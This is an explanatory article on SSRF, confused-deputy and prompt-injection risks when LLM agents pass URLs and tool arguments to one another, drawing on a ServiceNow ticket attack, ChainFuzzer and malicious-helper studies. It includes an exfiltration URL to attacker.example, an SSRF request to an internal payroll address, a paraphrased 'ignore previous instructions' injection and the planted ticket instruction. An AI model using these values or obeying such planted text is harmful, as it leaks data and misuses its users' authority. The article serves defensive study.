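# Security of URLs and tool-call arguments passed between cooperating language-model agents

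## How an address passes from one agent to another

A language-model agent is a program in which a language model chooses actions and carries them out through tools. Organisations increasingly run several agents on one task, with one reading documents, another planning the work and another fetching files or sending messages. These agents pass each other web addresses and other parameters, often written by someone outside the organisation. An address has no effect until an agent uses it in a request, and by then that agent may have no record of who wrote it. An attacker who controls the address can therefore choose where the request goes, or what it carries, without access to the agent that sends it.

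### Agents, tool calls and addresses

*Agent Data Injection Attacks are Realistic Threats to AI Agents* (Choi, Kim and colleagues, 2026) describes how an agent works. The agent's program keeps a running text, called the context, which begins with the developer's instructions and a description of the available tools. The program adds the user's request and sends the context to the model. The model returns either a final answer or a tool call, which is a structured request to run a function such as fetching a page or sending an email. If it returns a tool call, the program runs the function, adds the result to the context and sends the context back, and repeats this until the model returns a final answer.

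Each value filled into a tool call is an argument. The main argument of a call that fetches a page is the address, and a call that sends an email has a recipient, a subject and a body. *Authorization Architectures for Tool-Using AI Agents* (Surapani, Kakitapelli and colleagues, 2026), a review of 89 sources, treats the tool call as the moment when a system must decide whether to allow an action, because that is when a model's plan takes effect in the outside world.

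In a system with several agents, each agent runs the cycle, and the output of one becomes input for the next. A hand-off is the point where one agent passes a task, message or value to another. A value's source is the place where it first entered the system, such as a web page, a support ticket or the user's own request. Its sink is the operation where it takes effect. Provenance is the record of which sources contributed to a value.

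The syntax of web addresses, or URLs, follows a standard that Berners-Lee, Fielding and Masinter (2005) set out in *Uniform Resource Identifier (URI)*. Take this one:

`https://supplier.example/prices/october.csv?region=eu`

The scheme, `https`, names the protocol. The host, `supplier.example`, determines which machine receives the request. The path, `/prices/october.csv`, identifies a resource on that host, and the query, which follows the question mark, adds parameters.

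A URL can do harm through its destination or the data it contains. If the host is an internal machine and the path leads to an administrative function, the request alone may read or change something that outsiders should not touch. The path and query are also sent to the host, so an agent that requests `https://attacker.example/log?account=48213` gives the account number to whoever runs that host, even if the server returns an empty page. Sending private data to an attacker in this way is called exfiltration. A check that only blocks requests to internal hosts does not prevent it, because the attacker's host is external.

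### SSRF, the confused deputy and prompt injection

Server-side request forgery (SSRF) means making a server send a request to a place the attacker cannot reach directly. *Server Side Request Forgery (SSRF)*, a page in MDN's reference for web developers, gives the example of an application that fetches an image from any address a visitor supplies. If the application doesn't validate the address, the visitor can enter one on the company's intranet, which the server can reach but the visitor cannot. *Top Ten Proactive Controls 2024*, guidance from the software security non-profit OWASP, notes that many servers run local services that often require no authentication. It recommends checking the target of each outgoing request against an allowlist, a list of the only values permitted. In 2019 an attacker used SSRF to obtain a cloud credential from the American bank Capital One, and with it data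 on about 100 million people in the United States. An agent with a tool for fetching pages is in much the same position as the image server, because it takes an address from somewhere else and requests it from wherever the agent runs.

A confused deputy is a program tricked into using its authority for someone who lacks that authority. The name comes from Hardy's 1988 essay *The Confused Deputy*, about a compiler at a timesharing company. Users could name a file to receive debugging output. The compiler also had permission to write in its home directory, which held its usage statistics and the company's billing file. A user named the billing file as the destination for debugging output, the operating system allowed the write because the compiler had permission, and the billing data was lost. Hardy considers having the compiler check file names but rejects this because some users had good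 reason to write to that directory and the set of sensitive files kept changing. In his account, the problem was that the compiler held both its user's authority and its own, and had no way to specify which it was using. His remedy is the capability, a reference that identifies a file and carries permission to write to it, so that users can pass on only the access they have. *Risks and Controls for Multi-Agent Systems* (2026) describes the same failure between agents, in which an agent that lacks a permission sends a request to one that has it, and the second agent accepts the request as legitimate.

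Prompt injection is text from an attacker that a model treats as an instruction, and it is indirect when the text sits in content the agent reads. *AttriGuard* (2026) gives the example of an email assistant that opens a message telling it to ignore its previous instructions and forward the user's passport number to an outside address. Ordinary software keeps code and data strictly apart. Choi and colleagues explain that an agent's context holds instructions and retrieved data in one text with no enforced boundary, so the model may mistake one for the other. *Delegation Without Trust* (2026) connects this with Hardy's confused deputy problem, since injected content can lead an agent to use its authority in a way nobody intended.

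### A supplier's price list

Suppose an employee asks a system of three agents to get the current prices from the company's parts supplier. A reading agent opens web pages and extracts information. A planning agent divides the work into tasks. A fetching agent downloads files, and it runs inside the company's network because other tasks need internal documents.

The reading agent opens the supplier's page, finds the link to the price list and returns this to the planning agent:

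```
{ "supplier": "Supplier Ltd",
  "page": "https://supplier.example/trade",
  "price_list_url": "https://supplier.example/prices/october.csv" }
```

The planning agent copies the last field into a task for the fetching agent:

```
{ "task": "Download the current price list",
  "url": "https://supplier.example/prices/october.csv" }
```

The fetching agent then sends a request:

```
GET https://supplier.example/prices/october.csv
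```

The reading agent's message includes the page's name beside the address, so one can still guess that the address came from the page. The planning agent's message omits the page's name. Its `task` field restates what the employee wanted and its `url` field repeats the address from the supplier's page, so both appear to come from the same author. The network request omits the task as well. The employee never wrote the address and probably never saw it.

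Authenticating the sender does not recover the lost information. *Authorization Propagation in Agent2Agent Systems* (2026) explains that each interaction in a chain of agents is a new request, and the agent in the middle becomes the direct caller of the next one. The fetching agent can therefore verify that the planning agent sent the task without learning anything about the address. For this reason, Surapani and colleagues separate two graphs. The first records who holds authority and who passed it to whom. Here it shows a valid chain from the employee through the planning agent to the fetching agent. The second records where content came from, and it is the only one that includes the supplier's page.

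In the supplier example, the address's origin is lost because the message format has no field for it. Models that write free-text reports lose such information too. Wang and Mannby (2026), in *Only as Safe as the Weakest Agent*, planted forged records in a store of files and had agents answer questions from it. Each forgery predated the record it claimed to correct and lacked the accession line that genuine records had. When a strong model in Claude Code, Anthropic's coding agent, read the forged file directly, it noted the missing provenance in all 180 runs and adopted the false claim in one. When a weaker model read the files and reported back, its report mentioned the missing provenance in 96 of 180 runs, and the strong model adopted the false claim in 75.

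It is less clear how much of the harm came from the missing observation. Of the 96 reports that kept it, 21 still led to the wrong answer. When the forgery was an archivist's note, the reports lost the observation even more often (55 of 180 kept it), yet its absence did not predict wrong answers. Wang and Mannby call the analysis associational, and they tested records, not addresses. They also hypothesize that delegation removes the occasion to verify. The strong model averaged 6.3 tool-calling turns when it searched the store itself and 3.2 when it delegated. The hypothesis fits the supplier case well, because a planning agent that receives a field called `price_list_url` has little reason to go back to the page.

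Now let an attacker gain control of the supplier's page and change the target of the link to `http://10.0.4.17/payroll/export`. Addresses that begin with 10 work only inside private networks, so the attacker cannot request this one himself. The reading agent returns it as `price_list_url`, the planning agent copies it into the same task, and the fetching agent sends:

```
GET http://10.0.4.17/payroll/export
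```

If the payroll service trusts every machine on the network, it returns the payroll file. This is SSRF, with the fetching agent acting as the server. It is also a confused deputy problem, because the agent used its own access to fetch an address chosen by someone who had no access.

The attacker does not yet have the file. The planning agent receives it as a supposed price list, and it leaves the company only if a later step sends it out, for instance in an email asking the supplier about the prices. Requests to other internal addresses do damage immediately because the request itself triggers an action. To exfiltrate the company's secrets inside a URL, the attacker needs an agent to insert them, since he does not know them in advance. A link ending in `?account=YOUR_ACCOUNT_NUMBER` might be enough to make an agent do this, and a supplier's real website could reasonably contain such a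 link.

### Injected instructions and manipulated values

The attacker could instead have introduced the payroll address by leaving the link alone and adding a sentence to the page telling AI assistants that the price list had moved and that they must fetch it from `10.0.4.17`. That would manipulate the model, because an instruction would make it choose the address. The attack with the altered link used no instruction. The reading agent was asked to return the target of the price-list link, and it did so correctly. Even a model perfectly trained to ignore foreign instructions would have copied the address, because the attacker manipulated only the value.

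Several classifications are close to this distinction but do not quite match it. *CounterSteer* (2026) separates tool hijack, in which the attacker chooses the tool that the agent calls, from parameter manipulation, in which the attacker's content goes into an argument of the legitimate tool. *AttriGuard* likewise describes an adversary who needs only the tools the task already uses and attacks through the arguments of authorized calls. Both classify attacks by the resulting tool call. An injected instruction can also produce a bad argument, so a bad argument alone does not show whether anyone manipulated the model. Yang, Yang and colleagues (2026), in *SOK*, a survey of attacks on agents at run time, compare manipulated arguments to SSRF because the tool is correct and the credentials are valid, but nothing limits which arguments the task permits.

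Defences against injected instructions may not stop forged data. Choi and colleagues studied "agent data injection", in which an attacker imitates the format of a tool's output. For example, the body of an email might contain text that looks like the start of another email from a trusted colleague. The model then treats the forged sender as real while carrying on with the user's task. In a simulated office environment with GPT-5.2, a model of December 2025, injected instructions succeeded in 0.2% of attempts against an agent without additional defences, while data injection succeeded in 49.1%. A classifier built to detect injected instructions caught none of the 108 data injections. Wang and Mannby similarly found that models resisted an explicit instruction to automated readers wherever they tested it, but accepted several of the forged records.

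Data injection differs from faithful copying because the model mistakes untrusted text for trusted text. The supplier's altered link works without that mistake, so a defence inside the model has even less to detect.

Separating the reading agent from the planning agent gives only partial protection. Choi and colleagues also tested a similar design, in which a quarantined model reads untrusted content and returns values to a main model, which chooses the tool calls and never reads the raw text. This keeps hostile sentences on the page away from the main model, but data injection still succeeded in 25.0% of attempts because the quarantined model returned the attacker's values and the main model used them.

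### Checks on destination and origin

A destination check tests where a request is going. It blocks the altered link because `10.0.4.17` is a private address. A full check needs more steps, since a harmless-looking name can resolve to an internal machine's address. An allowlist containing only `supplier.example` would block both the altered link and `attacker.example`, but somebody would have to extend the list for every new supplier.

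An origin check tests where a request, or a value in it, came from. *From Agent Traces to Trust* (2026), a survey of provenance in agents, frames the question as whether malicious content influenced a later tool call or argument value. In the supplier example, a rule that agents may request only addresses the user wrote is too strict, because the employee did not write the good address either. Origin alone cannot distinguish the two links, since both came from the same page. A rule that combines origin with destination works, by allowing an address taken from the supplier's page to lead only to the supplier's host.

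Such a rule works only if the address's origin survives both hand-offs. The planning agent's message would need another field, such as `"url_source": "https://supplier.example/trade"`, and ordinary software should fill it in, because a model may omit it or accept a forged one. Choi and colleagues got Claude Code and two other coding agents to run an attacker's command by forging the author's name in a comment. They also found that one version of CaMeL, a defence that attaches origin labels to data, lost the labels when the quarantined model extracted values from a tool's response, and 23.1% of the data injections succeeded. A stricter version stopped all of them, but the agent then completed 36.5% of its ordinary tasks, compared with 86.5% with no defence.

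A final-request filter checks each finished request just before the system sends it, using only the request itself. Its advantage is that every request can be made to pass through it, whichever agent produced the address. In the supplier example, the filter receives `GET http://10.0.4.17/payroll/export`, so it can check where the request is going but not where the address came from. If the company also lets its payroll staff download that export through the fetching agent, the filter must either allow both requests or block both.

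## ServiceNow: a support ticket that recruited other agents

ServiceNow sells software that large organisations use to run help desks and other internal services. Its Now Assist product adds agents that read, sort and update the records. These agents find each other while they work, whereas in the supplier example someone had decided in advance which agent would pass work to which. In November 2025 AppOmni, which sells security monitoring for such platforms, described a test by Aaron Costello, then its head of security research. Costello planted an instruction in a support ticket. An agent that read the ticket brought in a second agent, and confidential text from another ticket ended up where the attacker could read it. The values Costello controlled were record numbers rather than web addresses, but they passed between agents in the same way.

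### The ticket and the two agents

Costello put two of ServiceNow's ready-made agents in a chat channel open only to an administrator. The first reads and summarises incident tickets to categorise them. The second, the record agent, can read, create and update records in any of ServiceNow's task tables, including the one for incidents.

He also created an ordinary user who could open tickets but couldn't read anyone else's. As this user, he opened ticket INC0000002 and wrote an instruction in its description for any agent that read it. The agent was to look up the description of another ticket, INC0000001, and copy it into INC0000002 before continuing its original task. If it couldn't do this alone, it was to look for agents that could.

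The attack began when the administrator had the first agent work on the ticket. The text of INC0000001 then appeared in INC0000002, which the ordinary user could read because he owned that ticket. ServiceNow's protection against prompt injection stayed on throughout. In what Costello calls second-order prompt injection, the attacker leaves the text in a record, and somebody else later has an agent work on it.

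| Operation | Agent with the permission | What the planted text determined | Authority used |
|---|---|---|---|
| Read INC0000002 | Either agent | Nothing | Administrator's |
| Read INC0000001 | Either agent | The record and the field | Administrator's |
| Update INC0000002 | Record agent only | The record, the field and where the new text came from | Administrator's |

The attacker didn't know what INC0000001 contained, so he could not write the new text himself. He specified where to find it and where to put it. In simplified form, which is not ServiceNow's own format, the last tool call amounted to this:

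```
{ "action": "update",
  "record": "INC0000002",
  "field": "description",
  "value": "(text copied from INC0000001)" }
```

An administrator may read and edit both tickets, so the access rules allowed the agent's actions. A destination check would probably have allowed them too, since the text went into the ticket the administrator had asked the agent to handle. It was a leak because that ticket's owner was not allowed to see the text.

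In other tests, Costello used more complex prompts to make an agent give a malicious user the administrator role. Where the system could send email, he also used it to extract data. AdExchanger's *How Agentic AI Can Break In The Real World*, based on an interview with him, describes a ticket that asked for someone else's data by email. There the recipient is one of the arguments the attacker chooses, so an allowlist of recipients might stop the message, though it would not have stopped the copying between tickets.

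### Borrowing the administrator's permissions

Both agents used the administrator's permissions because Now Assist agents, by default, act as whoever started the conversation. ServiceNow's *Implement access control in Now Assist AI agents* calls this identity the "dynamic user". The default is sensible because it limits what a user can get by asking an agent directly. If the ordinary user could have asked the record agent for INC0000001 himself, the agent would have had only his permissions and the request would have failed. By planting the text in a ticket, he could wait for someone with more permissions to have an agent read it.

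Unlike Hardy's compiler, the ServiceNow agents had no authority of their own to misuse, only the administrator's. Making an agent inherit its user's permissions stops the user from exceeding those permissions through the agent, but it doesn't stop a third person from using the agent to act with the user's permissions.

An organisation can instead run an agent as an "AI user", a separate identity with its own fixed roles. ServiceNow offers this for tasks that need permissions the person asking does not have. An employee can then start an agent with greater permissions than his own if the agent's access control list allows him to. The list does not limit what the agent can do once it has started.

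The identity that ServiceNow checks also changes along the chain. As in the supplier example, ServiceNow checks only the immediate caller, comparing each agent's list with the identity that caller ran under. If an employee starts an agent that runs as an AI user, and that agent calls another, ServiceNow compares the second agent's list with the AI user's roles, not the employee's.

### Three default settings

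Three default settings let the first agent find the second. The language model must support agent discovery, and both models on offer at the time did (ServiceNow's own, which was the default, and one supplied through Microsoft's Azure service). The agents must belong to the same team, and ServiceNow automatically puts agents that share an assistant on one team. Each agent must also be marked "discoverable", which ServiceNow does by default when someone publishes the agent.

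Two background components then arrange the hand-off. The ReAct engine manages the flow of information and delegates tasks. When it needs an agent, the orchestrator searches the team's discoverable agents for the most suitable one. The ticket therefore only had to describe work that required the record agent's permission, without naming that agent.

An administrator could easily miss what these settings allow. According to ServiceNow's *Select channels and status for an AI agent*, the administrator chooses which chat assistants may invoke a new agent, and choosing the same assistant for two agents puts them in one team. ServiceNow's *Managing AI agents in Virtual Agent Designer* defines a "discoverable" agent as one that a user's words can invoke, but Costello found that the same setting also lets other agents find it. ServiceNow lets agents collaborate because, according to its *Create an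 AI agent*, they can get better results with fewer calls to the language model.

The attack also needed the agents' tools to run without human approval. Costello writes that such attacks succeed only under this condition, so one of the main remedies is to require approval.

### ServiceNow's reply and the available fixes

ServiceNow told Costello that the behaviour was intended. It then updated its documentation to explain the risks of these settings more clearly (The Hacker News, 2025). According to AdExchanger, the company also emailed customers about communication between agents, crediting Costello and AppOmni, but left the feature on by default. Costello wanted it to be off unless customers switched it on.

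ServiceNow did quickly fix another of his team's findings, BodySnatcher, which let an attacker impersonate an account holder using only that person's email address. The different treatment has some logic, since BodySnatcher let a stranger get past an access rule, while every agent in the ticket test stayed within the administrator's permissions. But that means ServiceNow's access rules permit the leak, which makes its reply less reassuring. Customers have to prevent the leak through settings that, according to Costello, often take effect without their noticing.

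The evidence comes from a demonstration, which the AI Agent Index, a catalogue of agent products hosted at MIT, lists as risk research rather than an incident. AppOmni had a commercial interest in the research, which it published the same day it announced its monitoring product for ServiceNow agents. ServiceNow confirmed that the system behaves this way, which makes the central finding easier to trust. The confirmation doesn't show how often the attack works, and AppOmni gives no success rate.

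Costello first recommends putting powerful tools, such as those that change records or send email, in supervised mode, so that a person approves each action. He told AdExchanger that a human in the loop was the only real fix and acknowledged that it would undercut the automation. An agent that sorts hundreds of tickets is less useful if someone has to approve every update. Reviewers can also miss the problem, because "Update the description of INC0000002" looks normal coming from an agent working on that ticket. They will notice something wrong only if the screen includes the new text and they recognise that it belongs elsewhere.

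The system property `sn_aia.enable_usecase_tool_execution_mode_override` can cancel this protection by making supervised tools run autonomously. ServiceNow leaves it off by default, so customers need only check that nobody has turned it on.

Another remedy is to divide agents into small teams, each with only the agents needed for one kind of task. If the record agent had been in a different team, the first agent might still have read INC0000001, but it could not have recruited the record agent to write the text into the attacker's ticket. Agents can no longer get help from outside their team, so customers lose some of the flexibility that discovery offers. A planted instruction can still misuse the team's own capabilities. Costello also recommends monitoring, and suggests comparing the original task with the tools the agents used. For example, sorting a ticket should not normally involve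 rewriting its description.

Chen, a ServiceNow employee, writes that ServiceNow later added role masking, in its December 2025 release, and made it a required part of setting up an agent. Role masking restricts an agent to a chosen subset of the invoking user's roles, and the restriction carries over from a workflow to the agents and skills below it. According to ServiceNow's *Enable Role Masking for Agents*, agents inherit all of the user's roles unless a system property for role masking is set to true. The feature does not apply to agents that run as AI users.

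It would probably have prevented Costello's most serious result, the assignment of the administrator role, because an agent that manages tickets doesn't need the roles for managing users. Copying between tickets is harder to prevent this way. ServiceNow gives the example of adding the `itil` role to an agent so that it can read incident records. INC0000001 and INC0000002 are both incident records, so a role that lets an agent work on one may well cover the other. ServiceNow's *Agentic AI security and governance*, an index of its security controls from September 2026, lists role inheritance, activity logs and protection against prompt injection, but mentions no change to the discovery defaults.

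### When the request comes from another agent

Costello's test shows that one agent can pass an attacker's request to another, but not how readily the second agent will comply. Security researchers tested this in 2025 on 18 language models, including some from OpenAI, Anthropic, Google and Mistral. They tried to make an agent install malware through a tool that runs commands, and counted an attempt as successful when the malware connected back to the attacker's machine.

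The researchers tested three ways for an attacker to deliver the command. The attacker could give it directly to the agent, hide it as tiny white text in a document that the agent retrieved while answering a user's question, or rely on one agent to pass it to another. In the third case, which tested trust between agents, the first agent read the poisoned document but could not run commands, and it passed the command to a second agent that could.

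| Origin of the command, as the agent that ran it saw it | Models that ran it at least once | Share of model and prompt combinations that succeeded |
|---|---|---|
| A direct message | 17 of 18 (94.4%) | About three in four |
| A retrieved document | 15 of 18 (83.3%) | About six in ten |
| Another agent | 18 of 18 (100%) | About eight in ten |

The researchers tried six prompts on each model, running each prompt up to three times, and called a model vulnerable if a single run succeeded. The 100% means that every model failed at least once, not that every attempt worked. The difference between the second and third rows is still large. Gemini 2.5 Pro, Llama 3.3 and Llama 4 resisted all the poisoned documents, and Llama 4 also resisted the direct messages, but all three ran the command when another agent sent it.

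The researchers conclude that models apply laxer rules to other agents than to people or documents, and that trust between agents is the only factor that changed. Their set-up doesn't quite establish this, because two other things changed as well. The poisoned document surrounded the command with text that pressed the model to act at once or to ignore what it knew, which a model could recognise as an attack, while the first agent passed on only the bare command. The second agent's standing instructions also differed, describing it as an agent that others invoke to complete specific operations. It may have trusted the first agent, or it may have had less reason to be suspicious. Sending the same bare command directly from a user would help separate the two explanations. If the missing context explains the result, teaching models to be wary of other agents will help less than telling them where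 a request came from.

In a smaller experiment with three of the models, the researchers replaced the general command tool with one that could only run `ping`, a program that takes a machine's address as its argument and tests whether the machine is reachable. When an agent read the attacker's text itself, it put both the address and a malicious command into that argument, and the attack worked on all three models. When the request came through another agent, the receiving agent extracted only the address, and the attack failed. So a hand-off can sometimes remove an attack, if the receiving agent fills in a narrow argument and drops the rest. When the researchers used `find` instead, the attack succeeded on all three models even through a second agent, because `find`, a program for searching files, has a legitimate option to run commands on the results.

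These rates come from model versions dated November 2024 to July 2025, all more than a year old, and the researchers gave the models only a brief instruction to work securely. GPT-5.2, a newer model, resisted nearly all the injected instructions in Choi and colleagues' test, but it read the injected text itself, so the result does not show how a newer model treats a request from another agent.

### What the record agent could not see

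Even a better model in the record agent's place would have had little evidence of an attack. The request was to copy text from one ticket to another, and it came from an agent working for an administrator who could read the first and edit the second. Authenticating that agent would not have helped, because it was genuine. OpenAI's *Safety in building agents* recommends extracting only specific structured fields from outside content, so that injected text does not flow from one agent to the next. This would keep the planted instruction away from the record agent, but `INC0000001` is a valid value for a record-number field.

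If the request did include the value's origin, ServiceNow's software could combine it with information it already has about who opened INC0000002 and which tickets that user may read. A rule using this information has to apply when the agent updates a ticket, and it must consider where the copied text came from and who can read the ticket that receives it. Blocking the lookup of any record whose number came from someone without permission to read it would also block ordinary work. For example, a user might write that his problem resembles INC0000001 because a colleague mentioned that number, and the administrator would want the agent to look it up. The agent can safely show the administrator what it finds, but copying it into the user's ticket would disclose it to someone without permission to read it.

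## ChainFuzzer: tracing values through twenty agent applications

Costello found the route between ServiceNow's two agents by hand. In *ChainFuzzer*, Wu, Nan and colleagues (2026) describe a program that searches for such routes automatically, which they ran on 20 open-source agent applications. The program looks for chains of tools that can carry an attacker's value to a dangerous operation. It reads the tools' source code to work out where a harmful input might take effect, and it also uses fuzzing, which means testing software with many varied inputs.

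### Working backward from the sink

The applications had about 50 tools each, too many to test every combination. ChainFuzzer therefore starts with the sinks, searching each tool's code for calls to a fixed list of risky functions. These functions run system commands, execute code, query databases, render page templates or send network requests. The network functions include ordinary ones such as `requests.get`, a common way to fetch a page in Python.

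A tool that contains such a call may still be harmless. For example, nobody can redirect a tool that always fetches the same address. ChainFuzzer therefore traces the call's argument backward through the code and keeps the tool only if the tool's input can influence that argument. Of the 998 tools in the 20 applications, 199 met this condition.

*Beyond Predefined Sinks* (Cui, 2026) illustrates the problem with three tools that contain the same command-running call. The first passes the agent's value straight to the call, the second overwrites it with a constant, and the third checks it against an allowlist. A search for function names would treat all three alike. ChainFuzzer's rule excludes the second, but the third must be run to find out whether its check works.

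### Direct and indirect dependencies

From each sink tool, ChainFuzzer works back to the tools that could supply its input. In a direct dependency, one tool's output contains a value that another tool takes as an argument. For example, a search tool returns a `url` field and a download tool takes a `url`:

```
search("parts supplier price list")
  returns { "url": "https://supplier.example/prices/october.csv" }

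download(url="https://supplier.example/prices/october.csv")
```

The model reads the result of the first tool and writes the call to the second, so no code connects the two. ChainFuzzer finds the link by comparing the fields one tool returns with the parameters the other accepts.

In an indirect dependency, one tool stores a value in a file, database, search index or cache, and another tool reads it later. Wu and colleagues give the example of a user who asks an agent to find a patch for a bug. The agent searches the web, downloads a result, saves it as a script and runs it. Each step makes sense for the task, but together they let a stranger's web page supply code that runs on the user's machine.

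The supplier's price list could travel the same way. Suppose one agent saves supplier details in a file and another later downloads every price list named there:

```
write_file(path="suppliers.json",
           content='{ "price_list_url": "http://10.0.4.17/payroll/export" }')

download_all(list="suppliers.json")
```

The last call contains only a file name. Anyone who checks its arguments will see nothing wrong unless they also open the file, and the file may not record where the address came from. The network request that follows contains the address, so a destination check could still block it.

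Stored data can also reach the sink days after it leaves the source. *Ghost in the Agent* (Cai, Wen and colleagues, 2026) describes an agent that saves a confidential financial forecast in its long-term memory. Three days later, in a new session, a user asks for an operations report, and the agent retrieves the note and copies its figures into the report. An existing tracking system used for comparison failed to link the report to the forecast because its record of the source ended with the first session.

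ChainFuzzer's matching rules are deliberately broad, so they also connect tools that no sensible task would combine. It uses GPT-4o to judge whether an agent would plausibly use each chain for a realistic task, and discards the chains that fail. This left 2,388 candidate chains. The filter saves effort, but it may discard chains that an attacker could steer an agent into using.

Wu and colleagues examined ten of the remaining chains from each application by hand. They confirmed 714 of the 740 links between tools (96.49%), and every link was correct in 183 of the 200 chains (91.50%). So most of the chains ChainFuzzer lists are real, but the check did not measure how many real chains ChainFuzzer misses.

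### Running the chains

An agent may never follow a chain that exists in the code, so ChainFuzzer writes a request for each chain that asks the agent to use the tools in order. It compares the agent's tool calls with the intended chain and revises the request if they differ, for instance by telling the agent to create a file that a later step needs. It accepts the request once the agent has completed the chain five times in a row, which happened for 2,213 of the 2,388 chains. Wu and colleagues ran all 20 applications with the same model, GPT-5.1, whereas TicketOracle tests individual models against SSRF.

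ChainFuzzer then inserts a test value, called a payload, into the user's request or into outside content such as a web page or database record. If the model refuses the payload, ChainFuzzer changes it and tries again.

For SSRF, the payload is a URL that leads to an internal machine. ChainFuzzer confirms a vulnerability only if the payload influences the destination of a network call and the request resolves to an internal address or a designated test endpoint. This test is stricter than checking whether the model wrote the URL into a tool call, but it doesn't require the attacker to receive the response. In the supplier example, it would count the request for the payroll file even if the file never left the company.

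ChainFuzzer confirmed 365 vulnerabilities in 19 of the 20 applications. Of these, 302 needed several tools and 63 needed only one.

| Dangerous operation | Payload from the user | Payload from outside content | Total |
|---|---|---|---|
| Running a system command | 82 | 39 | 121 |
| Sending a network request (SSRF) | 44 | 53 | 97 |
| Executing program code | 53 | 26 | 79 |
| Querying a database | 29 | 16 | 45 |
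| Rendering a page template | 17 | 6 | 23 |
| All | 225 | 140 | 365 |

SSRF is the only type that began more often in outside content than with the user. Wu and colleagues explain that agents often take network addresses from pages they retrieve, as in the supplier example. But ChainFuzzer placed each payload according to the tools in the chain, so the split does not show which route real attackers prefer.

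When Wu and colleagues switched off chain extraction, ChainFuzzer found only 63 vulnerabilities, the same as the number of single-tool vulnerabilities in the full run. They take this as evidence that most findings depend on combinations of tools, but the test adds little evidence beyond the full run's count.

### What a confirmed vulnerability means

The tester steered the agent into every chain, so the counts show that the paths exist, not how often an attacker would succeed. In a sample of 200 chains, agents followed the intended chain in 27.05% of runs with the original request and in 95.45% with the repaired request. Without the repairs, ChainFuzzer found 96 vulnerabilities instead of 365. An attacker who controls only a web page cannot keep rewriting the user's request until the agent follows the intended chain.

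On SSRF vulnerabilities that ChainFuzzer had already confirmed, the initial payload worked in only 29 of 100 trials, even with the repaired requests. A real attacker might do better by adapting a page to one application, or worse because they can't predict what its user will ask.

The total of 365 vulnerabilities is also hard to interpret because Wu and colleagues do not explain what makes a vulnerability unique. Only 199 tools contained a reachable sink, so some tools must account for several vulnerabilities. If ten routes lead to one unsafe download tool and each counts separately, repairing that tool could remove all ten.

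This weakens the paper's claim that testing one tool at a time would miss most of the problems. A test of the download tool alone could show that it accepts internal addresses, but a tester needs the whole chain to find out whether a stranger's web page can supply one.

The severity of a finding depends partly on who runs the agent. In 225 of the 365 cases, the payload came from the user. Wu and colleagues consider a malicious user of an agent hosted on someone else's servers, where making it run commands would be a serious breach. A user running the agent on their own computer could often run the same command without it. Some of the 20 projects, including LangChain and LlamaIndex, are frameworks for building agents, so a path between their tools matters only where a developer has given an agent those tools.

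Cui's program found 23,866 potentially dangerous operations in 67 repositories of agent software, and it found evidence that an outside or agent-supplied value might influence 9,821 of them. Cui then reproduced 22 behaviours in 13 repositories using controlled tests. He classed one as a confirmed vulnerability, left another pending disclosure, and judged the other 20 not to be vulnerabilities because of protections or limits on how people use the software.

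Cui chose his cases for targeted testing rather than at random, so one in 22 is not an estimate of how many of ChainFuzzer's findings are real. His preprint also has not been peer reviewed. ChainFuzzer tried its payloads on running applications, so it would not have confirmed a finding if a check in the application had blocked them. It could not test the protections that each organisation adds around the software. Wu and colleagues acknowledge that an SSRF chain may fail if the network blocks outgoing requests or the internal service requires a credential. They also report no confirmations from the applications' maintainers, who might regard some of these behaviours as intended.

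### Tools that harvest or corrupt other tools' data

ChainFuzzer tests non-malicious tools that pass on an attacker's value. *Les Dissonances*, a study by Li, Cui and colleagues presented at the NDSS security symposium in February 2026, considers an attacker who has written one of the tools. Developers often import whole sets of tools from public repositories, and the model chooses which to call based on their descriptions. An attacker can therefore get a malicious tool called by describing it as helpful to another tool.

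For example, a YouTube search tool in LangChain expects its input as a comma-separated list. Li and colleagues built a tool for preparing this list, which agents called just before the search. The tool sent the query to the attacker's server, which could replace the search terms before returning the list. They also built a fake URL validator, which agents called before any tool that took a URL. A tool called at that point can return a different URL, which the next tool will fetch.

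The same trick can collect private data. A tool in these frameworks usually can't read another tool's results directly, but it can declare arguments for the model to fill in. Li and colleagues wrote a location checker that asked for the user's current physical address as well as the location in the query. If the agent knew the address from earlier work, it passed it to the tool. The address leaks through the argument, so a check on the URLs an agent opens would miss it.

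To measure how widely this works, they built Chord, a program that generates malicious helpers and tests them in running agents. They collected 281 tools from the LangChain and LlamaIndex repositories and tested the 66 they could run without paid accounts or elaborate set-up. For each tool, Chord used GPT-4o to write one helper to run before it and another to run after it, then tried each position on five tasks. If too few attempts worked, Chord rewrote the helper's description to make the model more likely to choose it.

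| Result | Tools affected, out of 66 |
|---|---|
| The agent called the malicious helper before or after the tool | 50 |
| The helper collected data related to the tool's task | 48 |
| The helper corrupted the tool's input or output | 45 |

A tool counted as hijacked if the malicious helper succeeded in only one of five attempts, but for more than half of the 50 hijacked tools, the helper succeeded in all five when it was designed to run first. The tests began with the helper already installed, so they do not measure how often developers would install one. Li and colleagues argue that developers could do so because public repositories do little to check tools for security.

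ChainFuzzer calls the 66 tools' failures vulnerabilities, although the search tool worked as it should. The weakness is in how the model chooses tools and trusts their output, so changing the search tool might not help. If a download tool accepts internal addresses, however, its developer can add a destination check.

Prompt-injection defences also had little to detect, because the helper returned ordinary-looking search terms or prices rather than suspicious instructions, much like the altered link on the supplier's page. In a test with ten of the hijacked tools, agents called the helper before the target in 77.78% of attempts without added defences and in 76.92% with a detector that examined tool output.

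Stronger models were easier to exploit. Helpers that ran first succeeded in 25.9% of attempts with Llama 4 Scout, 57.9% with GPT-OSS 120B and 75.2% with GPT-4o. The smallest model often called both tools at once, which broke the sequence the attack needed. All three models are now well behind the frontier. Better planning might make current models follow such sequences even more reliably, unless they have also become more likely to avoid unnecessary helpers.

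### From several tools to several agents

The 302 multi-tool vulnerabilities do not necessarily involve more than one agent, because one agent may call every tool in a chain. Wu and colleagues do not say how many chains crossed a hand-off between agents. Their 20 projects include MetaGPT, a framework for agents that work together, but they give no results for individual projects.

The analysis of sinks still applies to hand-offs because it concerns the tool's code. A download tool that accepts internal addresses will accept them no matter which agent calls it. Direct dependencies also remain when a message between agents preserves the relevant field, as the planning agent's message did in the supplier example.

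Stored values can pass between agents even more easily, because an agent can read a file that another agent wrote without the two exchanging messages, as long as both can access the same folder. Someone who monitors only messages between agents would miss this route. Cui lists messages from other agents among the sources that may influence an agent's behaviour, and notes that agent frameworks often hide hand-offs from ordinary code analysis.

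The success rates carry over less well. A single agent can keep the search result in its context when it calls the download tool, so it might notice where the address came from. A separate fetching agent may receive only the address, which could make an attack easier, especially if the fetching agent has access to the internal network and the reading agent does not.

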